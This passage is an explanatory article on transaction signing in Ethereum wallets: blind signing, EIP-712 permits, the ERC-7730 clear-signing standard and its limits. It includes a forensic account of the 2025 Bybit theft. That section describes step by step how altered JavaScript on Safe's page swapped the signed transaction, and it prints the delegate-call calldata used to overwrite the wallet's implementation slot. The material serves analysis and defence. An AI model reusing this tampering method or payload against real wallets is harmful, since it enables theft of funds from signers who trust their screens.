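Each line on the screen is accurate. The transaction carries no ether, Ethereum's own currency, because the payment happens inside the USDC contract. But "0 ETH" suggests that nothing valuable is leaving the account, and few people could find the payee in the data. The screen does not meet Weng's condition that it show all consequential facts.

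Some wallets display only a digest, from which nobody can tell what the transaction does. Trail of Bits, a security company that audits smart contracts, writes in *Implement EIP-7730 today* (2025) that a careful user would have to read the calldata on a workstation, check that its digest matches the one on the device, and then repeat the decoding on a second workstation. This takes several minutes per transaction, and Trail of Bits doubts that many people do it.

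Refusing to sign isn't always practical either. People who want to use a contract their hardware wallet can't decode have to switch on blind signing, according to *Add clear signing to your protocol with ERC-7730*, a tutorial on ethereum.org.

Trail of Bits prints an example of the raw data that wallets offer instead of a digest. It is five blocks of 64 characters, and nothing in it indicates the type of request. Decoded like the transfer above, it contains two addresses, the largest number that fits into a block, a zero, and a time on 30 December 2022. This is the layout of a "permit", a message that allows the second address to spend tokens belonging to the first. The largest possible number means that the amount is unlimited.

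### Typed messages

A permit is a message that the token owner signs without sending a transaction. Someone else can submit it to the token contract later, which saves the owner a step and a fee. Permits follow EIP-712, an Ethereum standard that divides messages into named fields with types. A permit's fields are "owner", "spender", "value", "nonce" (a number that prevents reuse) and "deadline". The signature covers these fields and the domain, a further part of the message that usually identifies the contract and network it is for.

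A wallet that supports EIP-712 can therefore display a list of labelled values. Trail of Bits considers this progress but not enough, because the values are still in the form the contract uses. The table follows Trail of Bits' example of a user exchanging ether for USDC.

| Field | Value in the message | Meaning |
|---|---|---|
| amountIn | 500000000000000000 | 0.5 ETH |
| amountOutMin | 800000000 | At least 800 USDC |
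| slippageBps | 100 | 1% tolerance for price changes |
| deadline | 1715157000 | 8 May 2024, 8:30 a.m. |

Even specialists can get these values wrong. In a second example, Trail of Bits evidently wanted to exchange up to 800 DAI, another dollar token, for 800 USDC. But it listed the USDC address first, and this function treats the first token as the one the user pays with. As printed, the request would exchange up to 800 trillion USDC for less than a billionth of a DAI. The mistake is harmless in an article, but a user would have trouble spotting it in the same fields on a wallet.

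EIP-712 also doesn't help with messages that contain another call. A field named "data" can hold calldata for a different contract, and the wallet shows that calldata as a long string unless it knows how to decode it. Trail of Bits' main example is the Bybit theft of February 2025, where one of the crucial changes was to the "operation" field, which went from 0 to 1.

Thieves also trick ordinary users into signing permits by presenting them as login requests. The crypto research firm Four Pillars, which may hold assets it writes about, cites figures from the security company Scam Sniffer on phishing sites that trick people into signing away their tokens. These sites took about $83.85 million from 106,106 victims in 2025, or about $790 each. In the eleven cases with losses above $1 million, permits accounted for 38% of the money. Victims who signed permits could have seen an address in a field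 called "spender", but the field name doesn't make it clear that the spender can empty the account.

### A descriptor for each contract

Ledger's first solution was separate software for each service. From 2021, developers could build a plugin that let Ledger devices decode one service's transactions. This worked but didn't scale, because every plugin needed someone who knew the hardware and kept the code up to date. Trail of Bits counted fewer than 200 dedicated Ledger apps in June 2025, many of them simple wallets.

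Castillo, Rein and colleagues (2024), in *ERC-7730*, replaced the plugin with a descriptor, a text file that explains a contract's functions to any wallet that supports the standard. Displaying a transaction in readable fields in this way is called clear signing. The contract itself doesn't change, so developers can add a descriptor years after publishing it. For the USDC transfer, a shortened descriptor could look like this:

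```json
{
  "context": { "contract": { "deployments": [
    { "chainId": 1,
      "address": "0xa0b86991c6218b36c1d19d4a2e9eb0ce3606eb48" }
  ] } },
  "metadata": { "token": {
    "name": "USD Coin", "ticker": "USDC", "decimals": 6
  } },
  "display": { "formats": {
    "transfer(address to,uint256 value)": {
      "intent": "Send",
      "fields": [
        { "label": "Amount", "path": "value",
          "format": "tokenAmount", "params": { "tokenPath": "@.to" } },
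        { "label": "To", "path": "to", "format": "addressName" }
      ]
    }
  } }
}
```

The wallet uses it as follows.

1. It checks that the transaction goes to the contract address and network listed under "context". If not, it must not use this descriptor.
2. It removes the argument names from "transfer(address to,uint256 value)", hashes the rest, and compares the first four bytes with the selector in the calldata. Both are a9059cbb.
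3. It splits the remaining calldata into an address and a number.
4. It formats each value as the descriptor specifies. "tokenAmount" applies the token's decimals and adds its ticker, and "@.to" means that the token is the contract receiving the transaction. "addressName" replaces an address with a name if the wallet has a trusted source for one.

The screen then shows "Send", "Amount: 1,500 USDC" and the supplier's name or address. Other formats turn numbers into dates, durations or words. A lending service can have its codes 1 and 2 shown as "stable" and "variable", and a descriptor can replace the number for an enormous spending limit with "Unlimited".

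Suppose the descriptor gave USDC 18 decimals, an easy mistake because ether and many tokens have that many. If the wallet relied on this figure, it would calculate

1,500,000,000 / 10<sup>18</sup> = 0.0000000015 USDC.

The contract would still transfer 1,500 USDC, because the descriptor affects only the display. A careful employee who expected to see 1,500 would stop. But a thief could use the same error to make a transfer of 1.5 million USDC look like 0.0000015.

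For this reason, Castillo and colleagues recommend leaving the token details out of the descriptor when the contract can report them, as the USDC contract can. But the ethereum.org tutorial tells developers to add them to any token's descriptor. The standard also contains the opposite error. One of its examples gives DAI six decimals instead of 18, so a wallet that copied the example would display one DAI as a trillion.

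Querying the contract isn't enough by itself, because a hardware wallet usually has no internet connection of its own. The response has to reach the wallet through the host, so the wallet needs some way to check that malware hasn't changed the response.

### Who vouches for the description

Under Weng's definition, a truthful display never relies on a description from the party requesting the action. ERC-7730 only partly meets this definition. The device takes the address and the amount from the calldata, but the word "Send" and the choice of fields come from the descriptor. The contract's developer usually writes the descriptor, because the developer knows best what the functions do. A dishonest developer can use the label "Claim reward" for a function that empties the user's account.

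Checking the contract address limits the damage a malicious descriptor can do. A descriptor for a thief's contract can't change how the wallet displays a USDC transfer, but it can mislead anyone who uses the thief's contract, for example by hiding the amount of a spending permission. It can also refer to a fake token named USDT, the name of a real dollar token.

Descriptors reach wallets through a public registry of files on the code-hosting site GitHub. Until 2026 the registry belonged to Ledger, whose security team reviewed each submission. Now automatic checks confirm that a descriptor is well formed, matches the contract's published code and includes at least one test transaction for every function. Maintainers also screen for malicious files. But these checks can't rule out misleading labels, and the tutorial warns that inclusion "does not imply audit or endorsement".

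That assurance is supposed to come from independent reviewers. Under *ERC-8176*, a companion proposal, an auditor who has compared a descriptor with its contract signs a digest of the descriptor, so a wallet can detect later edits to the file. Auditors can also revoke a signature. *Introduction to ERC-7730*, from Sourcify, a project that publishes contracts' source code, reports a first round of these attestations from the security company Cyfrin.

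Reviewers have little reason to take part, though. Four Pillars found no payment scheme for attestations. The Ethereum Foundation, a non-profit that supports Ethereum's development, announced $1 million in audit grants when it took over the registry, but these fund audits of the protocols themselves. Developers can also attest to their own descriptors, which proves where a description came from but not that it is correct. Participants in the discussion of ERC-8176 want wallets to label developers' attestations differently from reviewers' attestations.

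The wallet maker makes the final decision, because each wallet chooses its registry and the reviewers it trusts. It also has to protect the descriptor in transit to the device. In the standard's discussion thread, *EIP-7730*, one participant asked whether the design shifts the security model to "trust the host". It would if the device accepted any descriptor the laptop supplied, because malware on the laptop could then make the device's genuine screen show a false explanation. Castillo and colleagues therefore require wallets to ensure that nobody can alter the formatting in transit. Attestations are one way to do this, if the device checks them itself.

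Some critics think a central collection is the wrong approach. One participant in *EIP-7730* called such registries "honeypots" that let attackers deceive many users at once. *ERC-8283*, a proposal from June 2026, warns that the registry could become a bottleneck, because a contract without an entry would be effectively banned if wallets began to block blind signing. It proposes a registry on Ethereum itself that anyone can write to, with trust depending entirely on attestations. This would remove the gatekeeper but make the shortage of reviewers worse.

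### Nested calls, upgrades, gaps and small screens

The transfer above is a single function call, but many transactions pack several calls, such as a permission followed by an exchange, into the arguments of an outer function. ERC-7730 lets a descriptor mark an argument as embedded calldata, and the wallet then looks for a second descriptor that covers the inner call. If it finds none, or doesn't support embedded calls, it may show a digest of the inner call and the contract it goes to. The user is then blind signing the inner call, even though the outer call is readable.

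Even when all the inner calls are readable, the screen may not show how they depend on each other. Alex Forshtat, now one of the standard's authors, gave an example in the discussion thread. A user grants unlimited spending permission, exchanges 100 tokens and sets the permission back to zero. The individual steps look the same whether or not the network cancels all three when one fails. If it does, the user can't lose more than the 100 tokens. If it doesn't, a failed exchange can leave the unlimited permission in place.

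Forshtat also wanted a clear warning for delegate calls, which run another contract's code with control over the caller's storage and funds. Castillo had acknowledged earlier in the thread that the format didn't distinguish these from normal calls. According to Four Pillars, thieves took about $2.54 million in August 2025 through bundled transactions, in which a single signature approved several actions.

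Lists cause a related problem. A developer described a contract that makes many payments at once, some from the signer's account and some from money the contract already holds. Displaying every amount would overstate the cost to the signer, while displaying only the first could hide most of it. The correct display would include only the payments the signer funds, but under the standard's visibility rules, whether a field is shown can depend only on its own value, not on a neighbouring field.

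Another difficulty is that contracts can change. Many sit behind a proxy, a contract with a permanent address that forwards calls to a second contract containing the actual code. The owner can replace the second contract without changing the address. Castillo and colleagues recommend that developers put the proxy's address in the descriptor and update the descriptor after an upgrade, and that wallets use its latest version. Sourcify describes the rule differently, saying that descriptors always attach to the code behind the proxy, but the standard recommends this only where many user accounts share the same code.

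This relies on an honest and prompt developer. A dishonest one can wait for good attestations, then upgrade the contract so that its deposit function steals the deposit, while the selector, arguments and displayed text stay the same. The same can happen without an upgrade if the function is written to behave differently once the owner changes a stored value.

One participant in the thread proposed that descriptors list the stored values that a function's meaning depends on. Before signing, the wallet would compare them with the current values and, if they differed, warn the user or hide the readable text. The specification didn't include this as of November 2026. A hardware wallet has no internet connection of its own, so it would need a trustworthy way to get the current values.

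For a function with no descriptor, Castillo and colleagues advise wallets to display a label such as "Unknown function" with the raw arguments, and they forbid applying an unrelated description. This avoids misleading the user, but it returns them to blind signing. The fallback is most dangerous when attackers have taken over a contract that used to be safe. Reviewers can revoke their attestations, after which a wallet that checks them stops showing the readable text. Forshtat objects that users accustomed to blind signing will just continue, and proposes a separate status, "removed - malicious", with a warning. He seems right, because without that status a hijacked contract looks the same as an unlisted one, which may be harmless.

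Hardware wallets also have small screens and little memory. Ledger's *Design Rationale* explains that this is why the standard flattens fields into a simple list and discourages nested structures. Wallets with more room can show a single sentence, such as "Send 1,500 USDC to" followed by the supplier's name, while smaller devices can use the list. The sentence is easier to read but also easier to manipulate. Castillo and colleagues warn of a token whose name contains the words "to vitalik.eth", which makes the sentence appear to name a different payee. They require wallets to check names before inserting them, and recommend keeping the separate fields available.

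The standard also allows devices to shorten addresses, and gives 0x5aAe...eAed as an example. Even on an otherwise trustworthy screen, a shortened address can be hard to tell apart from the look-alike addresses that attackers use for address poisoning.

### Simulating the result

Clear signing shows what a transaction instructs a contract to do, while transaction simulation predicts the outcome by running the transaction on a copy of the network's current state. For the payment to the supplier, a simulation would show the company's balance falling by 1,500 USDC and the supplier's rising by the same amount. Simulation doesn't need a descriptor, and it can also reveal that a deposit function now sends the money to an attacker, even if an outdated descriptor still presents the call as a deposit.

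The result, however, usually appears on the host. Attackers exploited this to steal from Radiant Capital, a lending service, after putting malware on a developer's computer. According to Four Pillars, the developers checked the transactions in a simulation and in their wallet software, and saw nothing unusual in either. But the malware sent their Ledger devices a different call, transferOwnership(), which gave the attackers control of Radiant's lending pools. The devices couldn't decode the call, so the developers signed it without seeing what it did.

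Simulation can also mislead on an uncompromised computer, because the state of the network may change between the simulation and the transaction's execution. This is called a time-of-check to time-of-use (TOCTOU) gap. Suppose an attacker's website offers a user free ether, and the simulation correctly predicts that the user will receive it. Just before the user signs, the attacker changes a value in the contract so that the same transaction takes the user's money.

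Ledger and the journalist Inabinet, writing for the crypto publication Bankless, point out that a simulation can lack context. When someone moves tokens to another network, a simulation of the first network shows only that the tokens leave, which looks like a total loss. A descriptor can explain that the tokens are being transferred. Ledger has an interest in recommending descriptors over simulation, but their objection to simulation is sound.

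The two methods catch different errors, so using both makes sense. Forshtat argues that the hardware wallet should also display simulation results, with origin checks similar to those for descriptors. He also proposes letting users sign the outcome as a condition. The company could require that its balance fall by no more than 1,500 USDC, and the network would cancel the transaction if it fell by more. This would close the time gap because the approval would no longer rest on a prediction. But it requires either changes to Ethereum itself or an account that can run such checks.

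### Adoption by late 2026

According to Four Pillars, version 2 of ERC-7730 came out in April 2026 and added support for transfers between networks, encrypted amounts and sentences with inserted values. Ledger acknowledges that the first version was too closely tied to its own products. Competing wallet makers also had reason to hesitate while Ledger controlled the registry.

On 12 May 2026 the Ethereum Foundation took over stewardship. Its announcement, *Clear Signing* (Bruikman, 2026), adopts "what you see is what you sign" as the goal and credits Ledger with starting the work. Anyone may run their own copy of the registry.

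Ledger remains an interested party and used the handover to call its own devices the most advanced implementation, without offering a comparison (Ledger, 2026). It also claims that thieves stole more than $3 billion in cryptocurrency in 2025 and that a "significant portion" involved users approving what they couldn't read, but it gives no breakdown. The Bybit theft alone accounts for about half of the total.

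Coverage was small at the time of the handover. Four Pillars counted 346 descriptors from 44 protocols on 7 May 2026, including large ones such as Uniswap, Aave and Tether. Sourcify's collection has over 28 million verified contracts, according to its *Making Clear Signing the default on Ethereum*. Comparing the two counts makes coverage look worse than it is, since one descriptor can serve many contracts and people use a few contracts far more than the rest. The share of transactions that users can read would be a better measure, but neither source reports it.

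Sourcify also wrote at the launch that the specification was "no longer a draft to bet on", though it was still officially a draft in November 2026. These statements conflict less than they seem to, because each numbered version of the file format stays fixed once published. Version 1.0.0 is deprecated, 2.1.0 is current, and version 3 is in development. A developer can safely write a descriptor for version 2, but may have to revise it later.

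By August 2026, Sourcify listed working implementations from Ledger, Trezor and the software wallet Ambire. MetaMask, a software wallet that took part in the working group, wasn't on the list. A software wallet's display runs on the user's computer, so readable fields there help against a dishonest website but not against malware that controls the computer.

Ledger devices don't always show transactions with listed contracts in readable form. Ledger's *Clear Signing overview* states that transactions from another company's wallet appear in readable form only if that company has an agreement with Ledger. The standard is open, but Ledger decides which other wallets can use it on Ledger devices.

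## How the Bybit signers came to approve a tampered transaction

On 21 February 2025, three executives of Bybit, one of the largest cryptocurrency exchanges, used hardware wallets to approve what looked like a routine transfer between two of the company's own accounts. The transaction they signed gave thieves control of the sending account, and the thieves took about $1.5 billion within minutes. The thieves never had the executives' private keys, and every signature was valid.

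### A wallet that needs three signatures

An exchange pays withdrawals from a hot wallet, which is connected to the internet, and keeps most of its cryptocurrency in a cold wallet, whose keys stay offline. Bybit refilled its hot wallet from the cold one every two or three weeks, according to the Spanish-language news site CriptoNoticias, which summarised a livestream by Bybit's chief executive, Ben Zhou.

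The cold wallet was a multisignature wallet, or multisig, a smart contract that releases money only when a set number of signers approve (Curvegrid, 2025). Bybit's wallet required three approvals. The contract came from Safe, a company that also runs a free web page for preparing and signing transactions.

Rivas, Santos and Sanz (2025), in *In-Depth Technical Analysis of the Bybit Hack*, describe how a transfer from such a wallet works.

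1. One signer enters the transfer on Safe's web page. The page sends a message to the signer's hardware wallet, which signs it.
2. The page uploads the transfer and the signature to Safe's server.
3. The other signers open the same page, see the pending transfer and sign it on their own devices.
4. Once there are enough signatures, anyone can send them to the contract, which checks them and carries out the transfer.

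The message follows the EIP-712 standard for named fields. Alirun's *How to verify your Ledger signature of Gnosis Safe transaction* lists ten fields, four of which matter here. "To" is the address the wallet calls, "value" is the amount of ether, and "data" is the calldata. "Operation" is 0 for an ordinary call and 1 for a delegate call, which gives another contract's code control of the wallet. The remaining fields cover fees and the order of transactions.

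The signature covers a digest of the whole message, which software computes in two steps:

message hash = *H*(type | to | value | *H*(data) | operation | … | nonce)

Safe transaction hash = *H*(prefix | domain hash | message hash)

Here *H* is Ethereum's hash function, "type" identifies the list of fields, the prefix is two fixed bytes, and the domain hash identifies the wallet. Hashing the fields this way binds each signature to all of them, including "operation". The binding worked at Bybit, but the thieves got around it by changing the message before anyone signed it.

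### From a developer's laptop to Safe's web page

Safe hired the security firm Mandiant to investigate, and The Hacker News' *Hackers Stole $1.5 Billion in Bybit Heist* (2025) summarises the findings. On 4 February, a Safe developer downloaded a software project that posed as a stock investment simulator, probably after being tricked into it. The attackers then took over the developer's open sessions with Amazon Web Services, where Safe stored the files for its web page. They didn't need to pass multi-factor authentication because the developer had already done so. They worked during the developer's usual hours to avoid attention. They later deleted their malware and the command history from the developer's laptop, so it is less certain how they first got in than what they did afterwards.

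On 18 February, the attackers published two contracts on Ethereum that they would need for the theft, according to CertiK, a smart contract auditor. The next day at 15:29:25 UTC, they replaced one of the JavaScript files that Safe's website runs in a visitor's browser. That time comes from Verichains, one of two firms that investigated for Bybit, as quoted by The Daily Hodl (2025).

There is strong evidence that the file was replaced. Sikder (2025) reports in *Bybit $1.4 Billion Breach Linked to Safe Wallet Vulnerability, Investigation Finds* that public web archives saved the file twice on 19 February, first in its original form and then with the malicious code. Sygnia, Bybit's other investigator, found the altered file in all three signers' browser caches.

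For almost everyone, Safe's page still worked normally. Rivas and colleagues print the added code, which does the following:

1. It checks which Safe wallet the visitor is using and changes a transfer only if the wallet is one of two on its list. One was Bybit's cold wallet. Investigators couldn't identify the other, but think it probably belonged to the attackers.
2. It checks that the transfer is an ordinary call.
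3. It saves a copy of the transfer, then overwrites the address, amount, data, operation and one of the fee fields.
4. It sends the altered message to the hardware wallet.
5. Once the signer has approved, it restores the original transfer on the page but keeps the signature for the altered one.

Because of the last step, the page uploaded the routine transfer to Safe's server with a signature that didn't match it. The next signer also saw the routine transfer, and the script repeated the swap. It inserted the same fixed values each time, so all three signatures were valid for the same malicious transaction. Safe's server could have detected the mismatch after the first signature. Rivas and colleagues infer that it didn't check then, and found that it does now.

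The transaction ran on 21 February at 14:13:35 UTC, just under 47 hours after the attackers replaced the file. They submitted the transaction themselves, since the contract lets anyone submit one that carries valid signatures. Two minutes later they put clean files back on Safe's server, according to The Block's *Lazarus appears to compromise Safe developer machine* (2025).

### The transfer on the page and the transaction on the device

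The table compares the transfer the signers meant to approve with the message their devices received.

| Field | Safe's web page | Message sent to the device | What the message does |
|---|---|---|---|
| To | Bybit's own wallet | 0x9622…7242 | Uses a contract the attackers published |
| Value | About 13,000 ETH | 0 | Sends no ether in this step |
| Data | None | a9059cbb, an address and a zero | Calls that contract's "transfer" function |
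| Operation | 0 | 1 | Lets the function change the wallet's own storage |

CriptoNoticias took the 13,000 ETH figure from Zhou's livestream. The third column lists the values in the malicious code, but what the signers saw on their screens depended on their devices. Rivas and colleagues reconstructed the request on a Trezor Model T, a hardware wallet that can display the individual fields. A device that couldn't display them would have shown only digests or raw data.

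The data field has the same layout as the USDC payment in the previous section:

```
a9059cbb
000000000000000000000000bdd077f651ebe7f7b3ce16fe5f2b025be2969516
0000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000000
```

The attackers wrote the function called here and named it "transfer". It writes the address it receives, which starts with bdd0, into storage slot 0, the first place where a contract keeps its data, and it moves no tokens. To someone reading it as a token payment, the call looks like a transfer of zero tokens to that address.

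Bybit's wallet was a proxy, and its slot 0 held the address of the contract with Safe's actual code. The signers approved a delegate call to the attackers' "transfer" function, so the function overwrote slot 0 of Bybit's wallet. An ordinary call would have overwritten slot 0 of the attackers' own contract and done no harm. CertiK thinks the attackers chose the name "transfer" because a function called "upgrade" might have raised suspicion. Once slot 0 was overwritten, the wallet ran the attackers' code, which had one function for taking all the ether and another for taking tokens. Neither needed the signers' approval.

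The thieves took 401,347 ETH, about 31 times what the signers meant to move. They also took three kinds of token that represent ether. The Block's *How the largest crypto exchange hack happened* (2025) values the ether at $1.12 billion and the tokens at $253 million, $44 million and $23 million, for a total of $1.44 billion. Other estimates range up to $1.5 billion. The Hacker News reported that only 3% of the stolen funds had been frozen by early March.

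### What the signers checked

Zhou was the last of the three to sign. By his account, all the signers saw the correct address on the page, and he confirmed that the page's URL was Safe's official one. Checking the URL couldn't reveal the attack, because the page came from Safe. The website's own server delivered the altered code, unlike in the browser attacks on bank customers.

Only Zhou's Ledger device could have warned him. CriptoNoticias reports that its screen didn't clearly show the destination, only a block of code, which he checked "not completely in detail". CertiK, summarising the same livestream, writes that he didn't verify the data on the device at all. Blockworks' *Profiting from disaster* reports that he admitted he didn't verify it fully. The difference hardly matters for the outcome, since most people couldn't tell where the money was going from a partial look at a block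 of code.

There is less evidence about the other two signers. Communications of the ACM's *Behind the Bybit Crypto Theft* quotes Andrew Fierman of Chainalysis, a company that traced the stolen money, as saying that Bybit's signers approved without checking the full details on the device. That agrees with Zhou's account of himself, but it comes from an investigator rather than the signers themselves.

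Oman Observer's *A $1.5 billion hack* (2025), a reprinted New York Times article, reports that Zhou was finishing some work at home in Singapore that evening when he approved the transfer. Half an hour later, the company's chief financial officer called to tell him the ether was gone. "I should have paid more attention on this area," Zhou said of Bybit's defences.

### Why three signatures gave little extra protection

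A multisig protects against the loss of one key and against one dishonest employee. It would also protect against false displays if each signer used different software. Suppose an attacker has a 1 in 100 chance of compromising any one program. If three signers use three unrelated programs, the attacker has a 1 in 1,000,000 chance of compromising all of them. If they all use the same web page, the chance is 1 in 100, the same as for a single signer.

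The three signers had separate hardware wallets, and nobody has reported that the attackers tampered with them. Each wallet gave its owner a chance to refuse the transaction, but the usefulness of that chance depended on whether the owner could read the screen. If each signer had an even chance of noticing the change, all three would miss it one time in eight. If the screen was so hard to read that each had only a 1 in 50 chance, all three would miss it 94% of the time. These probabilities are invented, but they show why adding signers doesn't make up for an unreadable display.

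Signing with colleagues can make a person less careful. The last signer sees that two people have already approved and may assume that they checked. CriptoNoticias suggests that Zhou may have relied on the multisig process, though he didn't say so. engn33r, Piña and colleagues write in a guide to signing that a multisig's security depends on each signer verifying independently.

The code may also have influenced who signed. It reloaded the page for two particular signer addresses, which would have interrupted anyone using them to approve a transfer. Rivas and colleagues don't explain why. Perhaps the attackers expected those signers to notice something.

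### Safe's server or Bybit's signers

On the day of the theft, most specialists suspected that Bybit's computers had been compromised. The Block reported a growing consensus among security researchers that malware had infected the signers' machines, and Safe had found no sign of a compromise in its official web page. Trail of Bits' *The $1.5B Bybit Hack* (2025) made the same assumption. Charles Guillemet, chief technology officer of Ledger, agreed, though he called this speculation in Blockworks' *Bybit attack shows ‘fundamental’ need for institutional-grade security*.

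The forensic reports reversed that view within a week. Bybit (2025) announced that neither Sygnia nor Verichains had found any compromise of Bybit's infrastructure, and that stolen credentials from a Safe developer had let the attackers "totally deceive signers". Bybit was paying both firms, which is a reason for caution, but Safe confirmed, against its own interest, that the attack came through its developer's machine.

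Safe's statement still left out a lot. Safe maintained that the attack hadn't compromised its frontend or source code, although its server had delivered malicious code to signers' browsers. The wording may mean that the original code in Safe's files was intact, but that didn't protect anyone using the page. Changpeng Zhao, the former head of the exchange Binance, complained in The Block of "vague language" and asked how the attackers had got past the Ledger check with several signers, and whether the signers had signed blind or failed to verify the transaction.

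Guillemet blamed blind signing and told companies to "stop signing blank cheques". His company, Ledger, sells custody systems to businesses, so he had a commercial reason to recommend something more expensive than Safe. Ledger was also partly responsible for the screen Zhou couldn't read. Blockworks reports that Ledger had removed blind signing in June 2024, which seems to conflict with Zhou's description of what his Ledger device displayed eight months later.

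Bybit's signers could have checked the transaction more thoroughly, but the procedure was difficult. Schubotz's *How to verify Safe transactions on a hardware wallet*, one of Safe's guides, warns that "There is currently no easy UI-way of doing this" and that the steps require technical knowledge. That makes it less surprising that an executive approving a routine transfer skipped them. The difficulty doesn't excuse the company, which was responsible for as much as $20 billion of customers' deposits and could have hired someone to do the check or written software for it.

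Zhou later accepted part of this criticism, telling the New York Times that Bybit should have moved from Safe to a better system, according to heise's *Biggest theft in history*. Safe's chief product officer responded to such criticism by saying that large organisations rely on its products. Safe also called the difficulty of verifying a transaction an industry-wide problem, which is true, but the attackers reached the signers through Safe's server.

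Weng's conditions for an approval make it easier to divide the responsibility. Safe's page did not meet the condition of truthful rendering, because it displayed one transaction and sent another to the device. At least in Zhou's case, the device did not show all the consequential facts in a form he could use. Bybit decided to rely on that page and device to protect a $1.4 billion wallet. Either an untampered page or a readable device screen that the signers actually read would have prevented the theft.

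There is less dispute about who stole the funds. The FBI's *North Korea Responsible for $1.5 Billion Bybit Hack* (2025) attributes the theft to North Korea and calls the activity "TraderTraitor". Mandiant reached the same conclusion in its work for Safe. The FBI notice doesn't set out its evidence, but ZachXBT, an independent investigator, had already linked the theft to the same group through test transactions and connected wallets.

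### Which remedies would have worked

Some remedies proposed after the theft would have shown the signers what had changed, while others would have blocked the transaction even with three valid signatures.

| Remedy | Reveals the change to the signers? | Blocks the signed transaction? |
|---|---|---|
| Device that displays the message fields | Yes, if they read them | No |
| Digest recomputed from the intended transfer | Yes, if they compare it | No |
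| Wallet contract without delegate calls | No | Yes |
| Delay before execution | No, but others can inspect it before it runs | Only if someone cancels in time |
| Clean computer for signing | No | No |

#### A readable device screen

On a device that displays the fields, the signers would have seen an unfamiliar address, an amount of zero and an operation of 1, which means a delegate call. Rivas and colleagues consider the operation the most important, but note that it could have looked normal. On 14 January, Bybit had used a genuine delegate call to transfer mETH, one of the tokens the thieves later took.

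The amount was a better clue for someone without technical training. The signers expected to send thousands of ether, and a line reading "value: 0" would have contradicted that. But a signer would still have had to compare the screen with the intended transfer and be prepared to stop a routine payment over the discrepancy.

Decoding the inner call would have helped only if the device also checked which contract was being called. A device that recognised only the selector a9059cbb could have translated the attack into "Send 0 tokens", which sounds harmless. A wallet that follows ERC-7730 also checks the contract, so it should label the attackers' function as unknown.

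#### Recomputing the digest

If a hardware wallet can show only a digest, a signer can check it by entering the address, amount and other fields of the intended transfer into a program on another computer. The program outputs the domain hash and the message hash, which the signer compares with those on the wallet before approving. At Bybit, the message hashes would have differed.

The program must get the transfer from somewhere other than the suspect page. pcaversaccio's *Safe Multisig Transaction Hashes* offers a script that by default downloads the details from Safe's transaction service. In the Bybit attack, this would have worked for the second and third signers, because the malicious code had uploaded the original transfer to the service. The script would have computed that transfer's digest, which would not have matched the one on their devices. The first signer couldn't have used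 the script this way, since there is nothing to download until someone has proposed the transaction.

Attackers who expected this check could upload the tampered transaction instead. The digest from the script would then match the one on the device, and the signer would have to spot the change in the downloaded fields. Lido's *Safe Tx Hash Verifier for Mitigating UI Spoofing Risk* therefore requires the digest to be computed from the intended parameters, and offers a web app that works offline. OpenZeppelin's *Safe Hash Preview* describes a similar tool that takes manual input by default.

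This only moves trust to other software. *safe-tx-hashes-util* lists what users of pcaversaccio's script must still trust, including the script itself, the operating system, Safe's service and Ledger's screen. The comparison also depends on careful reading. Each digest has 64 characters, and if a signer compares only the two ends, an attacker can vary an unimportant field, such as a fee limit, until those ends match the expected ones, as with look-alike addresses.

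Another guide by Safe recommends comparing the transaction in three places: Safe's page, a simulation by the service Tenderly and the hardware wallet. The signer starts the simulation from the page, so it is not an independent check. A malicious page could send Tenderly the original transfer, and the simulation would then show the result the signer expected. Of the three, only the hardware wallet would have shown data that didn't match the original transfer.

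Bybit could presumably have done a more thorough check before a routine transfer, because its team managed one during the crisis on the night of the theft. Bybit needed to move $3 billion in stablecoins, which are tokens tied to an ordinary currency, to cover a rush of withdrawals. The team wrote software to verify the signatures "on a very manual level", as Zhou put it in Cryptonewz (2025).

#### A ban on delegate calls

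The attackers needed a delegate call to replace the wallet's code, so a contract that blocked such calls would have rejected their transaction even with three valid signatures. Rivas and colleagues suggest that Bybit could have used a simpler contract that only transferred ether and tokens. Such a contract could also have given the signers a readable message. Bybit would have lost little, though it would have needed a different way to make token transfers like the one on 14 January.

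Even with a ban, the attackers could have used their control of the page to change the recipient and amount of an ordinary transfer, so that the signers sent all 401,347 ETH to the attackers' own address. To prevent that, the contract would also have to limit the amount or accept only listed recipients. The list could be very short for a cold wallet that mostly refills one other wallet.

Rivas and colleagues also propose an internal service that checks transactions against a company's rules. If the service read the pending transfer from Safe's server, it would have seen and approved the original transfer. If it checked transactions just before Bybit submitted them, the attackers could have bypassed it by submitting the signatures themselves, as they did. To stop the attack, the service would have to hold one of the required signing keys and check the exact message it signs, or the contract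 would have to enforce the rules.

#### A delay

According to The Block, Safe pointed out that Bybit could have enabled timelocks, which delay changes to a wallet's configuration. A delay gives people time to inspect a transaction after it becomes public and before it takes effect, though it doesn't make the signing screen any clearer. Bybit learned of the theft about half an hour after Zhou had signed, when the money had already left. Bybit refilled the hot wallet only every few weeks, so it could easily have planned for a one-day delay.

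The delay would have had to cover delegate calls in general. If it applied only to the wallet's official functions for changing settings, an attack through a function named "transfer" might have gone through at once. Someone would also have had to decode the waiting transaction and cancel it. And if cancelling required three signatures through the same web page, the attackers could have tampered with the cancellation too.

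#### A clean computer

Much of the advice after the theft concerned the signers' laptops. CertiK recommended stricter protection, a separate computer just for signing, and a freshly installed operating system for important transactions. These measures can help against malware on the signer's machine, but at Bybit the malicious file came from Safe, and a brand-new laptop would have downloaded it as soon as the signer opened the page.

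The browser could have checked that the file was the one Safe had originally published. Rivas and colleagues say this would have stopped the attack if the attackers could change only the JavaScript, but not if they could also change the page that tells the browser which file to expect. A signing program that doesn't load its code from Safe's server each time avoids that weakness, but the company has to trust whoever supplies the program and its updates.

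### Radiant Capital and WazirX

Similar attacks had taken place before the one on Bybit. Trail of Bits groups the Bybit theft with earlier thefts of $230 million from the Indian exchange WazirX in July 2024 and $50 million from Radiant Capital in October 2024. It says that in all three, attackers made people see something different from what they were signing. Check Point had also publicly warned in July 2024 that attackers were misusing the function through which a Safe contract executes transactions.

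At Radiant, the malware ran on the developers' computers. According to CertiK, the attackers got it there by posing as a former contractor and sending a zipped file over the messaging service Telegram. A clean laptop would therefore have helped at Radiant, but not at Bybit.

A contract-level ban on delegate calls would not have prevented the Radiant theft, because the transferOwnership() call that Radiant's developers signed doesn't need one. A contract-enforced delay on ownership changes could have given Radiant time to respond. In both the Bybit and Radiant thefts, comparing the device's digest with one computed from the intended transaction would have revealed the swap.

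The WazirX case is weaker evidence for any particular remedy. Trail of Bits grouped it with the Bybit theft, but did so on the day of that theft, when it still believed that malware had infected the Bybit signers' own devices.

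## Building an agent's approval prompt from the parameters of its call

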